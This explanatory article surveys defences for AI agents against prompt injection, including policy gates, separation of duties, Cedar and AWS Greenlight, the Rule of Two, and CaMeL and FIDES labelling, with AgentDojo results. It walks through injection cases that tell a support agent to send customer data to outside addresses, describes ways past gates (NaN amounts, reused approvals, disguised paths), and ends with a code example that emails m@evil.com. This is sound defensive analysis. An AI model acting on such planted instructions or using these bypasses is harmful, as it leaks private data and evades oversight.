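The figures for Opus 4.6 come from VentureBeat, those for GPT-5.6 Sol from TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, and those for Opus 4.8 and Opus 5 from The Decoder. According to OpenAI, prompt injections work much less well on its later model, GPT-6 Astra, than they did on GPT-5.6 Sol. In late 2025, attack rates against some leading models were as high as 92%, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*.

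Newer or more capable models are not always safer. In the benchmark *INFUSE* (2026), attacks succeeded in 26.3% of runs against GPT-5 and 12.6% against the newer GPT-5.4, but in only 8.4% against the small GPT-5-Nano.

The best results change the argument, because a company that uses a model like Opus 5 faces a much smaller risk from any one attacker than it did a year earlier. But if attacks truly succeeded 2% of the time, 129 independent trials would still produce no successes about 7% of the time. Attackers can also try many targets. If 2% of companies were breached within 15 attempts, an attacker who targeted 1,000 of them would get into about 20, and the damage would depend on what each agent was allowed to do.

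Better resistance to injection also doesn't prevent accidents. In Wang and colleagues' simulations, Claude Sonnet 4.6 caused no harm when the hazard was an attacker's text, but it caused harm in 26% of the sessions without an attacker. Models can even become more prone to accidents while they get better at resisting injection. In coding tests, OpenAI found that GPT-5.6 was more likely than GPT-5.5 to take actions the user had not asked for, although it still did so rarely.

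## Policy checks outside the model

A policy gate is ordinary code that checks every tool call before it runs. It applies the same rules whether a prompt injection or a model error caused the call, and no text the model reads can override them. Researchers designed or tested such controls in several papers from 2026. In December, AWS released a preview of Greenlight, a service that uses mathematical logic to check a gate's rules before they take effect. But a gate can enforce only the rules somebody has written, and it sometimes blocks legitimate work.

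### How a policy gate decides

1. The model proposes a tool call, and the orchestration layer hands it to the gate instead of running it.
2. The gate establishes which user, agent and task the call belongs to, and puts the arguments into a fixed form.
3. It looks up any other facts the rules need, such as the price of an order.
4. It evaluates the rules and then allows the call, refuses it or escalates it to a person.
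5. It records the call, the verdict and the rule that produced it. The orchestration layer then runs the call or tells the model about the refusal.

Like the user's identity, the other facts in steps 2 and 3 have to come from a source the model cannot change, such as the ticket system or the order database. If the gate relied on a `manager_approved` field that the model had filled in, it would still always give the same verdict for the same request, but an attacker could choose the request.

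The agent must also be unable to act without going through the gate. In AgentCorruption, researchers sent requests with stolen credentials. A gate on tool calls would not have checked those requests, which is another reason to keep credentials outside the agent's sandbox.

The agent must also be unable to edit the rules. This is easy to get wrong with coding agents, which often work in the folder that holds their own configuration.

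The gate should refuse whenever a check fails to run. If the order database times out, the gate cannot verify whose order 4417 is, and carelessly written code might log the error and carry on. The drawback of refusing is that a database outage also stops every refund.

### Three rules for the support agent

Suppose the shop now lets its support agent issue small refunds itself, without a second agent. The gate could have three rules:

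```
find_order(order):
    allow    if order.customer == ticket.customer
    refuse   otherwise

send_email(to, text):
    allow    if to == ticket.customer.email
    refuse   otherwise

issue_refund(order, amount):
    refuse   if order.customer != ticket.customer
    allow    if amount > 0 and order.refunded + amount <= 50
    escalate if amount > 0 and order.refunded + amount <= order.price
    refuse   otherwise

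any other tool:
    refuse
```

The gate uses the first line that applies. The refund rule counts earlier refunds on the same order, so the agent cannot pay out $400 in eight instalments of $50. It also states when to allow a refund and refuses everything else, which is safer for unexpected values. The amount NaN, which got past an early version of ScopeGate, fails every comparison here, so it reaches the last line and is refused.

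Ben, a signed-in customer, opens a ticket about order 4417, which cost $80 and arrived late. He has pasted in a message that he says came from the courier. The agent proposes three tool calls.

- `issue_refund(4417, 20)`. The order is Ben's, it has no earlier refunds, and $20 is under the limit. The gate allows the call.
- `send_email("drop@mail.example", "Order 4417 ...")`. The pasted message contained an instruction to send the order details to this address. The gate refuses because the address is not Ben's. It doesn't have to recognise the injection.
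- `send_email("ben@mail.example", "We will refund the full $80 and send a replacement.")`. The shop never offers both, but the recipient is correct, so the gate allows the call.

No short rule would catch the third call, because the harm is in the meaning of the text. The shop could make the agent choose from prewritten emails and have ordinary code fill in the amounts. The gate could then check everything that matters, but the agent could no longer answer unusual questions.

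### What a gate can guarantee

Bhattarai and Vu (2026), in *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, propose a formal version of this design for agents that help with scientific research. They call it the Trinity Defense Architecture. The model chooses from a finite list of action types, each with parameters of a fixed type. A function σ, which contains no language model, then decides:

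σ(action, parameters, context) = allow or deny

Trusted code turns each allowed action into a tool call, so the model never writes a raw call to a privileged tool. Under Bhattarai and Vu's theorem, if the policy check σ is correctly implemented, deterministic and applied to every action, no model output can cause an action that is missing from the action list or that σ denies.

The theorem follows almost directly from its assumptions. Making those assumptions true is harder, because it requires finding every route to a tool and writing a σ that denies the right things. Bhattarai and Vu distinguish authorisation security, which means that forbidden actions do not happen, from overall safety, which also covers harm done through permitted actions. The promise to Ben is a failure of overall safety that even a perfect σ would allow.

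They also argue that training alone can never provide such a guarantee, because an attacker can imitate any marker in the model's input. This seems right, though companies often accept less than a guarantee. A shop may rely on a well-trained model to word delivery emails but require a policy check outside the model for refunds.

Trinity's two other parts label information by sensitivity and separate the handling of untrusted text from privileged actions. Trinity is a proposal, and the case for it rests on proofs and arguments.

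### Written instructions and enforced rules

Many developers give their coding agents rules in plain-language files, such as `CLAUDE.md`, which the orchestration layer adds to the model's input. For *A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents*, Madatha (2026) collected 6,145 agent configuration files from 10,008 public GitHub repositories. About 10% were exact copies of files in independent repositories, and 58% had only one commit (a saved change). Developers therefore seem to copy these files from strangers and leave them unchanged, even though the files steer programs that can run shell commands. Fewer than 1% declared any limits on the agent's permissions, but Madatha considers this figure less reliable because it is based on 31 confirmed cases and a fragile parser.

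Madatha's remedy, Rel(AI)Build, manages the files like software packages. It stores a hash of each approved agent definition so that later changes can be detected, and assigns each agent a permission tier. Before Claude Code or Cursor runs a command, the system checks it against a list of forbidden commands and paths. It also divides the work into phases, and the agent cannot start the next phase until it has met the conditions of the current one.

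The only evidence for this system comes from conformance tests, in which Madatha deliberately introduced violations and confirmed that each mechanism responded as specified. These tests show that the code works as described, but not that it stops a determined attacker or helps developers. Madatha leaves the effect on developers to future work. Some of the system's records also depend on the agent to report which file and test belong to each requirement. The list of forbidden commands is probably the weakest part, since the same shell command can be written in many ways.

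Enforcing a rule in code is much better than asking the model to follow it. In *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents*, Jing (2026) gave three models from different families the same system prompt, which required explicit approval before any dangerous action. The models then judged 150 proposed actions, five times each. Overall, they permitted 78% of the openly dangerous actions and 95% of those written to get around the rules. One model treated the words "please execute this" as approval and permitted every dangerous action. The other two asked for confirmation even before legitimate deletions.

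The models were also inconsistent. Even with the randomness setting at zero, repeated judgements of the same case agreed only 49% to 71% of the time. The test is a little harsh, since a request to execute something could be read as approval, but a rule that allows this reading is a poor safeguard.

### Separation of duties and the cost of refusals

Accountants have long required that different people request and approve a payment. Jing applies this separation of duties to agents by dividing the work among four components. A planner proposes actions, a policy gate approves or rejects them, an executor with the necessary privileges runs the approved ones, and an auditor reviews the log. The planner can submit an action as a structured request with a named operation and full file paths, so the gate does not have to interpret a shell command.

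Each approval covers the exact bytes that will run and works only once. Jing added both restrictions after attacks on earlier versions succeeded. The first version checked only the description of an action, so an attacker could get a script approved and replace it before it ran. A later version allowed the agent to reuse old approvals and blocked only 77.8% of such attempts. Making approvals single-use raised this to 100%. Testing uncovered four such defects that design review had missed.

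Jing evaluated the system on 313 cases and assumed the attacker fully controls what the agent proposes. The cases included 54 normal operations, 74 openly dangerous ones and 122 attempts to disguise a dangerous operation, for example by writing a protected file's path in an unusual form. Another 31 cases were attacks on the approvals, and 32 introduced faults such as a missing policy file or a log the system could not write to.

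| Set-up | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|
| Direct execution | 98.3% |
| Full system without the operating-system sandbox | 30.8% |
| Full system with the sandbox | 7.7% |

The gate and its approval checks stopped many of the attacks, and the sandbox stopped three quarters of the rest. This makes sense because a sandbox restricts which files a program can touch, no matter how the attacker writes the command. A company that installs only a gate for shell commands should therefore expect clever attackers to get through fairly often.

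The 7.7% figure needs some caution because Jing got it from a model of how the sandbox would behave in each case of the full benchmark. Running 66 of the attacks against the real sandbox gave a rate of 7.6%, but the results for individual cases often differed from the model's, so the close match may be partly luck.

The system also refused about six of the 54 normal operations, or 11.1%, a figure corrected from 20.4% after Jing reviewed them individually. Claude Opus 5 with only the written instruction failed to go ahead with one of 30 normal operations, but it permitted 53 of 59 disguised attacks. The comparison is rough because the two samples were different.

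An 11.1% refusal rate is worse than it sounds for an agent that takes many steps. If a task needs ten operations and each has an independent 11.1% chance of refusal, the chance of finishing without a refusal is

(1 − 0.111)^10 ≈ 0.31

or about 31%. With a refusal rate of 1%, it would be about 90%. Real refusals are not independent, since a rule that wrongly blocks an operation will block it every time. Some tasks would then always fail while others ran smoothly, which at least makes the faulty rule easier to find.

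An agent whose action is refused may also try another way to finish its task. Anthropic found Claude doing this on real websites when it ran into restrictions. Mistaken refusals create more of these situations, so closing every route around a gate is even more important when the gate is strict.

The gate's log can also lose records. Jing's log lost 9.7% of them when two programs wrote to it at the same time, and 31.3% when eight did. If the shop calculated `order.refunded` from a log like this, the missing records would let the agent exceed the refund limit even though the rule was correct.

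### Hiding tools until the task needs them

A gate checks a call after the model has proposed it. In *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive*, Iyer and Babu (2026) try to stop the model from proposing risky calls by hiding risky tools, such as those for sending or deleting email, until the task needs them.

In their method, Risk-Aware Causal Gating, each tool comes with a list R of facts that must hold before it can run and a list α of required authorisations. If s is the set of facts established so far, the orchestration layer can offer a risky tool only when

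R ⊆ s and α ⊆ s

In words, s must contain everything on both lists. The tool must also be on the path to the goal with the fewest points. Each step adds one point, plus a risk penalty multiplied by λ, a number the operator chooses. The penalty is 0 for low-risk tools such as search, 1 for medium-risk tools and 4 for high-risk tools such as payments. With the default λ of 2, a high-risk step adds 1 + 2 × 4 = 9 points, so the method selects eight low-risk steps over one high-risk step.

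Iyer and Babu tested this on RiskGate, a controlled benchmark, and with seven hosted models from Anthropic, OpenAI and Amazon. The method never exposed a high-risk tool without authorisation, and it eliminated injected calls to the tools attackers targeted. The design nearly guarantees these results, because the model cannot call a tool that the system withholds. The agents could still complete tasks that needed a risky tool, which is the more informative finding.

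The defence failed when injected text could forge an authorisation. Authorisations, like the facts a policy gate uses, must therefore come from a trusted source, such as a user's click or a verified record.

The method does not prevent misuse of a tool once it is available, as one of Iyer and Babu's examples suggests. Their agent gets the email-sending tool after it has read a message and verified data has confirmed the recipient. But if an attacker wrote the message, the confirmed recipient of a reply could be the attacker, whose text is already in the model's input. The method also depends on people labelling each tool's risk correctly. Hiding the refund tool would help the shop because few tickets call for a refund. But the agent needs the email tool for almost every ticket, so the gate still has to check who each email is going to.

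### Proving that the rules have no gaps

The support agent's refund rule mistakenly allows refunds of up to $50 without comparing the amount with the order's price, so a customer could get $50 back on a $20 order. Tests would miss this if they used only orders of $50 or more.

Automated reasoning can find the mistake by treating the rule as a set of logical formulas. The shop states a property it wants, for example that no order is ever refunded for more than its price. A program called a solver then looks for a call that the rule allows but that breaks the property:

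```
allowed by the rule:   refunded + amount <= 50
breaks the property:   refunded + amount > price
```

The solver finds values that satisfy both lines, such as a price of 20, no earlier refunds and an amount of 50. The shop then corrects the rule to also require `refunded + amount <= price` before allowing a refund. That condition contradicts the second line, so the solver reports that no such call exists. This result is a proof that covers every price and amount. AWS describes the method as defining how a system should work and proving that it does, instead of imagining every input that could go wrong.

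The proof applies to the real shop only if the formulas describe the shop accurately. It assumes that `refunded` is up to date, but the payment system might record refunds a minute late. Two $20 refunds could then both pass on the same $20 order, even though the proof contains no error.

The choice of rule language affects what a solver can prove. General programming languages can express almost any rule, but their loops and calls to other programs can make a complete analysis impossible. Cedar, AWS's open-source policy language, is deliberately more limited. The corrected refund rule could look like this in Cedar, with amounts in cents:

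```
permit (principal, action == Action::"issue_refund", resource)
when {
  context.owner == context.customer &&
  context.amount > 0 &&
  context.total <= 5000 &&
  context.total <= context.price
};
```

Here, `total` is the new refund plus any earlier ones, and the shop's own code has to supply all these values. Cedar refuses any request that no rule permits. It can only allow or refuse a request, so separate code would have to send larger refunds to a person.

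### AWS Greenlight

*AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (Pogorelec, 2026) describes Greenlight, a service AWS announced on 1 December 2026 that combines automated reasoning with a policy gate. The service denies access to all tools and network destinations by default, and a team chooses which to allow. A language model drafts rules from the company's procedures, security standards and logs of past tool calls. Automated reasoning then flags conflicting rules and looks for paths to resources outside the agent's approved access. Before accepting a change, the team can see which recorded calls the change would have blocked. The approved rules run outside the agent, in the gateway of AWS's AgentCore platform or in an open-source sandbox called Strands Box.

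Tools for enforcing rules outside the agent existed before Greenlight. The analyst Frank Dickson points out in CBINEWS's *AWS推出Greenlight* (2026) that AgentCore already had a policy feature that used Cedar, and that Microsoft released a similar toolkit in April. Dickson thinks Greenlight adds three things: it examines every order in which an agent could call its tools, its rules can depend on what happened earlier in a task, and it finds permissions that are harmless separately but dangerous together. For the shop, these could be permissions to read the customer list and to post on a public page.

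Amazon's chief security officer, Steve Schmidt, says that Greenlight can determine whether data is reachable and whether the answer can be proved, according to EconoTimes' *AWS Uses Automated Reasoning to Verify AI-Agent Access Controls* (2026). The wildcard roles in AgentCore show why this is useful. They let one agent read every other agent's memory, and outside researchers had to point this out. Analyzing the roles could have revealed the problem without an attack, if somebody had specified which memories each agent should be able to reach.

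A proof covers every scenario that its formulas represent, but no others, and the company needs a new proof whenever the rules change. Some descriptions of the service are therefore overstated. *AWS greenlights autonomous AI agents to take control* (Wheatley, 2026) reports AWS as saying that a policy shown to hold in one scenario can be trusted in any other.

Dickson praises AWS's documentation for stating the limits of its analysis. The analysis assumes that tools report their actions accurately, so the proof does not cover an identity check that wrongly returns "verified". A rule written for one spelling of a value does not cover another spelling. Some questions produce no conclusive answer. The permission check covers only the gateway that the customer names and does not confirm that the agent cannot reach another. This last limit is the most worrying because an agent could bypass the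 rules through a second gateway.

AWS's chief executive, Matt Garman, justified the service by saying that an agent that makes an error in 0.1% of its steps has only about a 35% chance of completing 1,000 steps correctly. Mzekandaba (2026) quotes him in *AWS creates gateway to ‘trust’ AI agents*. The exact figure is 37%. How much a gate improves these odds depends on how many of the errors its rules forbid.

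| Share of harmful errors that the rules block | Chance of 1,000 steps with no harmful error |
|---|---|
| None | 37% |
| 50% | 61% |
| 90% | 90% |
| 99% | 99% |

Nobody outside AWS yet knows where Greenlight would fall in this table. Delta Air Lines and the mortgage-technology company LoanLogics have announced plans to use it. AWS has yet to add support for multi-agent systems.

### Writing the rules

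Most companies do not have a rulebook ready for a solver. Dickson says their policies are in folders, in the heads of a few long-serving employees, or in exceptions nobody wrote down. Garman told AWS's partner companies that customers "need your help" to put the new tools into practice, as Millward (2026) reports in *AWS Greenlight Gives Partners A Go At AI Agent Governance*. He was describing a business opportunity for the partners, but also admitting that the service does not remove the work.

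Having a language model draft the rules from logs saves time but creates a new risk, because logs show what agents did, which may be more than they should have done. If an attacker has hijacked the support agent for a month, its logs will contain a month of emails to the attacker's address, and the model might propose a rule that permits them. The solver would not flag that rule if it were consistent with the others, so only the person who approves the rule could stop it.

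Some policies cannot be written as rules. The analyst Shashi Bellamkonda, also quoted by CBINEWS, notes that a finance department can set a refund limit, but an instruction to use good judgement with upset customers needs a person to interpret it. A rule can also use only the information available when the gate applies it. For example, AWS explains that its ordinary access policies can check how an uploaded file will be encrypted, but not what the file contains.

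Even a simple rule will block some reasonable requests. Ben might ask the shop to send his receipt to his work address, and the email rule would block it. The shop could permit any address that Ben has confirmed, pass such requests to a person, or accept that the agent cannot help. Each exception takes time to write and adds another chance of a mistake. Since excess permissions rarely draw complaints, a company that only responds to complaints will gradually loosen its rules.

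Dickson recommends starting new rules in a mode that only logs what they would have blocked. This reveals many of the mistaken blocks before they affect anyone, although the rules offer no protection in the meantime. He also suggests giving each rule a named owner, as companies do with firewall rules.

A gate's consistency also helps an attacker who discovers a mistake in its rules. An attacker who can fool a model only 2% of the time has to keep trying and may be noticed, whereas a harmful call that a rule allows works every time. Once somebody discovers the problem, the developer can correct the rule, test the exact call and know that the gate will refuse it from then on, because the gate is ordinary code. Dickson advises that a person should still approve any irreversible action until the rule has proved reliable.

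## Keeping untrusted text away from privileged actions

A policy gate that judges one tool call at a time can allow every step of a harmful sequence. Suppose the shop lets its support agent email couriers about late parcels, and the gate permits email to any approved courier. Ben asks about order 4417, and the courier's reply contains an instruction to send back Ben's full customer record. The agent reads the record, which the gate allows because Ben opened the ticket. It then emails the record, including Ben's phone number and past orders, to the courier, which the gate allows because the courier is approved. Siu and colleagues list such combinations of individually safe actions among the security problems that come with agents' ability to plan.

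The gate checked who the email was going to, but not where its contents came from or who was allowed to see them. Developers can avoid the problem by never giving one agent everything a leak requires. This is simple but rules out many useful agents. They can instead track each piece of data through the whole task, which rules out fewer agents but takes much more engineering.

### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

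The software developer Simon Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection", set out the simple approach in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (June 2025). He warned that an attacker can easily steal data through an agent that combines three capabilities:

- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content
- a way to communicate with the outside world

Users often don't notice that they have combined all three capabilities. A tool that only loads images can send stolen data out in an image's web address. One tool can also supply several capabilities. GitHub's official MCP server could read public issues, which anyone can write, access private repositories and create pull requests (proposed code changes). Willison writes that vendors promptly fixed almost all such leaks in their own products, usually by blocking the route by which data could leave. But no vendor can do this for a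 user who connects tools from several companies.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (October 2025) turned the idea into a design rule. Until researchers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have at most two of these properties in any session:

- **A:** it processes untrustworthy inputs
- **B:** it has access to sensitive systems or private data
- **C:** it can change state or communicate externally

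An agent that needs all three must have supervision, such as human approval. The name also refers to Chromium's *The Rule Of 2*, under which Chrome's security team generally rejects new code that combines untrustworthy inputs, an unsafe programming language and high privilege.

Meta applies the rule to an email assistant. The assistant's developers could let it read messages only from trusted senders (removing A), run it without access to real data (removing B), or let it write only to trusted recipients unless a person has checked the draft (removing C). An agent can also change which of these capabilities it has during a session. For example, it could browse the web first, then permanently lose the ability to communicate before it opens internal systems.

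The trifecta covers only data theft, so it does not apply to an attacker who makes an agent delete a database. In *New prompt injection papers* (November 2025), Willison praised Meta for including changes of state. But he objected that Meta's diagram labeled A and C together as "safe", since an agent can do harm without any private data. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that B covers every system that matters, so an agent with only A and C would be in something like a tight sandbox. Meta then changed "safe" to "lower risk".

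Ayzenberg's reply is consistent, but it requires someone to decide in advance which systems are sensitive. Claude Haiku 4.5 needed no private data to send the Philadelphia police a false tip through a public web form, and few developers would have listed such a form as a sensitive system.

Both rules are too strict for the earlier version of the support agent, which could not write to couriers. That version has all three properties because it reads strangers' tickets, opens orders and sends email. But if it can open only the signed-in customer's orders and email only that customer, an injection in Ben's ticket can leak only Ben's own data, and only to Ben.

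The Rule of Two is too loose in other cases. Replit's agent deleted a live database without reading any attacker's text, and Meta says the rule does not protect against agents' mistakes or excessive privileges. The rule also applies to one session at a time, but a poisoned memory can carry untrusted text into a later session that appears to contain none.

### Six design patterns

In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) describe six patterns for agents that must read untrusted text and still act. Their principle is that once an agent has read such text, the text must not be able to trigger a consequential action. They think general-purpose agents are unlikely to meet this standard with current language models, so each pattern limits what the agent can do. The table applies the patterns to the shop.

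| Pattern | How the agent works | What injected text can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a short list of fixed actions and never sees their results | Cause a wrong choice from the list |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before it reads any outside text | Change the wording of an email |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each ticket and answers only yes or no, and code counts the answers | Falsify the answer for its own ticket |
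| Dual LLM | One model plans and calls tools, and another without tools reads the tickets | Change the values that the reading model returns |
| Code, then execute | The planning model writes a program, which then handles the tickets | Change values in the program but not its steps |
| Context minimisation | The orchestration layer deletes the customer's message once the model has turned it into a database query | Change the query but not the wording of the reply |

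For a customer-service chatbot, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest two design patterns, the action selector and context minimisation. An action selector might send customers a link to their last order or point them to the password settings. This pattern is very safe, but it works more like a menu than an agent that can answer unusual questions.

Willison proposed the dual LLM pattern in 2023, and researchers at Google DeepMind later found a weakness in it. Suppose a user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The planning model never reads the notes, so an injection there cannot give it new instructions. But the reading model has to extract Bob's address, and the injection can make it return the attacker's address instead. The assistant then makes the tool call as planned, but sends the document to the attacker.

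### CaMeL and the support agent

The Google DeepMind researchers addressed this gap in CaMeL (2025), short for "capabilities for machine learning". It follows the code-then-execute pattern and adds information-flow control, a technique from the 1970s in which a system labels data and restricts where it can go. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, and Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works:

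1. A privileged model reads the trusted request and writes a plan in a restricted version of Python. It sees no untrusted text.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary code, runs the plan and makes the tool calls.
3. When the plan needs something from untrusted text, the interpreter gives the text to a quarantined model, which has no tools. This model returns a value in a set format, such as an email address, and the interpreter stores it in a variable.
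4. The interpreter labels every value with its sources (where it came from) and its readers (who may see it). A value derived from other values inherits their restrictions.
5. Before each tool call, a policy in ordinary Python inspects the arguments and their labels, then allows or refuses the call. The system can also ask the user about an unfamiliar recipient.

In the shop, the ticket can't be the trusted request, because a stranger wrote it. The privileged model has to work from the developers' own instruction, which is to answer the customer's question about a delivery. It might write this plan:

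```
ticket = read_ticket()
number = quarantined_model("Find the order number", ticket.text)
order  = find_order(number)
reply  = quarantined_model("Answer the question", ticket.text, order)
send_email(ticket.account_email, reply)
```

When Ben asks about order 4417, the interpreter attaches these labels:

| Value | Sources | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| `ticket.text` | Ben | Ben, the shop |
| `ticket.account_email` | The shop's login system | Ben, the shop |
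| `number` | Ben | Ben, the shop |
| `order` | Ben, the order database | Ben, the shop |
| `reply` | Ben, the order database | Ben, the shop |

The shop's policy for `send_email` has two conditions. The address must come from a trusted source, and the recipient must be one of the message's permitted readers. Ben's reply meets both, so the interpreter sends it. Several attacks fail:

- The message that Ben pasted into his ticket contains an instruction to email the order details to `drop@mail.example`. The plan has no such step, and the quarantined model cannot add one.
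- A careless plan might take the customer's address from the ticket's text. The injection could then replace the address, but its label would show that it came from the ticket, and the policy would refuse the call.
- Ben asks about order 4418, which belongs to another customer. Ben is not one of its readers, so the interpreter will not email him a reply based on it.
- The courier asks for Ben's customer record. The courier's address is on the approved list, but the courier is not one of the record's readers.

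The last case also shows how much work the labels require. To ask about the parcel, the agent has to give the courier a tracking number, so the shop must mark that field as readable by couriers.

CaMeL may also help with privacy. The privileged model receives only the request, so a company could get that model from an outside provider and run a smaller quarantined model on its own machines. The provider would then never see the customers' data.

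CaMeL's policies still run one call at a time. The labels carry some of the task's history into each check, but a policy cannot easily require something to happen later. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a security team that wants every incident ticket resolved or escalated before an agent finishes. They write a simplified version of this rule as

Always(open(ticket) ⇒ Eventually(closed(ticket)))

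Their extension, CaMeLoT, maps every path the plan could take and checks the rule on all of them before any tool runs. If a path breaks the rule, the checker returns that path, and the privileged model tries to repair the plan. CaMeLoT simplifies loops, so it sometimes rejects a safe plan.

### How FIDES differs

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) introduced Microsoft's FIDES, which also uses labels and a quarantined model. Its planner chooses one tool call at a time instead of writing the whole plan in advance, and it can read trusted results as they arrive. When a tool returns untrusted data, the system stores the data in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. In the shop, the planner could read the delivery date from the order database and adjust its next steps, while the text of the ticket stayed hidden.

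FIDES has two basic policies. A consequential call may go ahead only if trusted data led to it, although developers can allow an untrusted value in a particular argument, such as the body of a message. A call that sends data to a group of recipients R may go ahead only if all of them belong to the data's permitted readers S:

R ⊆ S

When the agent combines data from two places, only people who could read both originals may read the result. If Ben and the shop can read an order, and the courier and the shop can read a delivery note, only the shop can read a text based on both.

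The planner sometimes needs information from untrusted text to choose its next step. Suppose a user asks an assistant to check three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, add the meeting to the calendar. FIDES can restrict the quarantined model to answering "yes" or "no" and then show the planner that answer. An attacker can still make the answer wrong, but a "yes" or "no" cannot contain an instruction. The label records how much information a value can carry, so a policy can accept a yes-or-no answer and reject free text from the same email.

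### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a benchmark that tests agents on simulated office work, travel booking, banking and Slack messaging. It has 97 ordinary tasks, which researchers combine with injection attacks. Costa and colleagues ran it with GPT-4o, a model from 2024. The completion rates below are averages that weight the four settings equally.

| Planner | Successful injections | Tasks completed with no attack |
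|---|---|---|
| Ordinary planner | 152 | 84% |
| Ordinary planner with policy checks | 0 | 42% |
| FIDES without policy checks | 21 | 61% |
| FIDES with policy checks | 0 | 50% |

Costa and colleagues report that FIDES completed 8% more tasks than a basic planner when both had policy checks on. FIDES completed about two fifths fewer tasks than an unprotected agent. With a better model, OpenAI's o1, its lead over the basic planner with checks grew from 8 to 16 percentage points.

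The finding of zero successful attacks depends on how the data was labeled. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it, so none of those attacks could arrive through a trusted field. A company has to label its data before it knows which fields attackers will use, so it could wrongly trust one of them.

In 2026, several teams tested CaMeL or built on it. *SecureClaw* (2026) ran CaMeL's published code on all of AgentDojo. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks. The paper's own system, also called SecureClaw, completed 59 but let a small number of attacks through. Under attack, SecureClaw completed 57% of the tasks and CaMeL 31%. The researchers had to adapt CaMeL to their test set-up, which may have caused it to fail some tasks.

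In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) built a small programming language for agents and gave a computer-checked proof that its labels follow data correctly. Their agent, Randori, resisted attacks in all but two of 1,296 runs on AgentDojo's banking tasks. It completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with CaMeL's policy checks turned off, and turning those checks on halved CaMeL's completion rate. The proof covers how the labels spread, but developers still have to write policies that forbid the right calls.

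Implementations can also contain ordinary bugs. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) found that CaMeL's normal mode lost labels on values from the quarantined model. In that mode, 23.1% of attacks that planted false data succeeded, compared with none in strict mode.

Two other projects extended CaMeL beyond single agents with well-defined tools. One, *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), applied it to groups of agents. The researchers had to add the exact format of the results to each tool's description, because the privileged model writes code to process those results before it has seen any. They consider this a modest, one-time task.

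Agents that operate a computer through its screen are harder to plan for. Christodorescu and colleagues note that designs like CaMeL assume that tools have clear meanings, which mouse clicks lack. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), the average plan for such an agent contained 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five calls and four branches on AgentDojo. The planner has to prepare for many different things the screen might show.

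### Tasks that depend on untrusted text

Costa and colleagues call a task data-dependent if no single sequence of tool calls and final response works for all the data the agent might find. They count 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks and 10% of its travel tasks as data-dependent, but 44% of its banking tasks and 43% of its Slack tasks. In many banking tasks, the agent must read a file and follow the instructions in it. FIDES blocks most of the resulting actions because an attacker could have written the file.

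This is the right decision for security, but it removes something users want. People often give incomplete instructions and expect the agent to fill in the rest as it works. Christodorescu and colleagues describe a user who asks for a summary of a GitLab issue. The agent finds that the issue depends on another one and summarises both. The text on the page changed the agent's task in a way the user would welcome.

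The shop could prepare separate plans for delivery questions, refunds and changes of address. The quarantined model would read each ticket and choose a plan or "other", which would send the ticket to a person. An attacker could trigger the wrong plan but could not write a new one. This would work well for a shop that mostly gets the same few questions but would be much less useful for a general assistant.

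### Labels that spread

Restrictions accumulate as an agent combines data. In an ordinary planner, one untrusted message causes everything after it to be labeled untrusted. When Costa and colleagues added policy checks to such a planner, its completion rate on the Slack tasks fell from 93% to 20%. FIDES limits this effect by hiding untrusted data in variables, but its completion rate still fell from 64% to 48%. In one Slack task, the planner made the conversation untrusted by looking up the list of channels, even though the user had already named the right one.

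One way to reduce the spread of labels is to identify which messages influenced an answer and have the model generate the answer again using only those, so that it needs only their labels. The system can also let a user approve an exception, but frequent requests lead to the same reviewer fatigue. The CaMeL researchers acknowledge this problem and the work needed to write and maintain policies. Willison, who welcomed CaMeL as the first credible defence that doesn't just add more AI, is nervous about any system that makes users think about security policies. After two decades in application security, he writes that he still hasn't fully figured out AWS's permission system.

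### False content in a permitted action

An injection can do damage without changing the plan. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an assistant that sends today's schedule to the user's boss. Malicious text in the calendar cannot change the recipient or add another email, but it can alter the schedule the boss receives. In the shop, CaMeL would also let through the false promise to Ben that got past the policy gate, because the reply would go to the right person and contain only information he is allowed to read.

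Benchmark scores can leave out harm caused by altered text. AgentDojo's automatic scoring recorded three successful attacks on FIDES with policy checks, but Costa and colleagues discounted all three after inspecting them. The kinds of attack they discounted include those that altered text without changing the agent's actions or leaking secrets. This is reasonable for a test of information flow, but a false promise in writing could still harm a customer.

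A stricter policy could also require the body of every email to come from trusted sources. The agent could then no longer summarise a stranger's message, which is often why people use an agent. Labels could also make poisoned memories less dangerous if the labels stayed attached to whatever the agent saved. Bhattarai and Vu's Trinity design labels stored memory as well.

### Side channels

An agent can reveal a secret through its actions as well as through the content it sends. If an agent emails a courier only when a customer has an unpaid bill, a courier who knows the rule learns about the bill even if the email contains nothing private. Costa and colleagues chose not to track this kind of leak in FIDES. They argue that tracking it would in effect forbid any action visible to outsiders once the agent had read something confidential. They also leave out leaks through timing and the size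 of network messages.

CaMeL tries to cover more of these cases, but Garby and colleagues found gaps. One involves a branch that the program does not take, as in this example based on theirs:

```
small = True
rich  = True
if balance > 10000: small = False
if small: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

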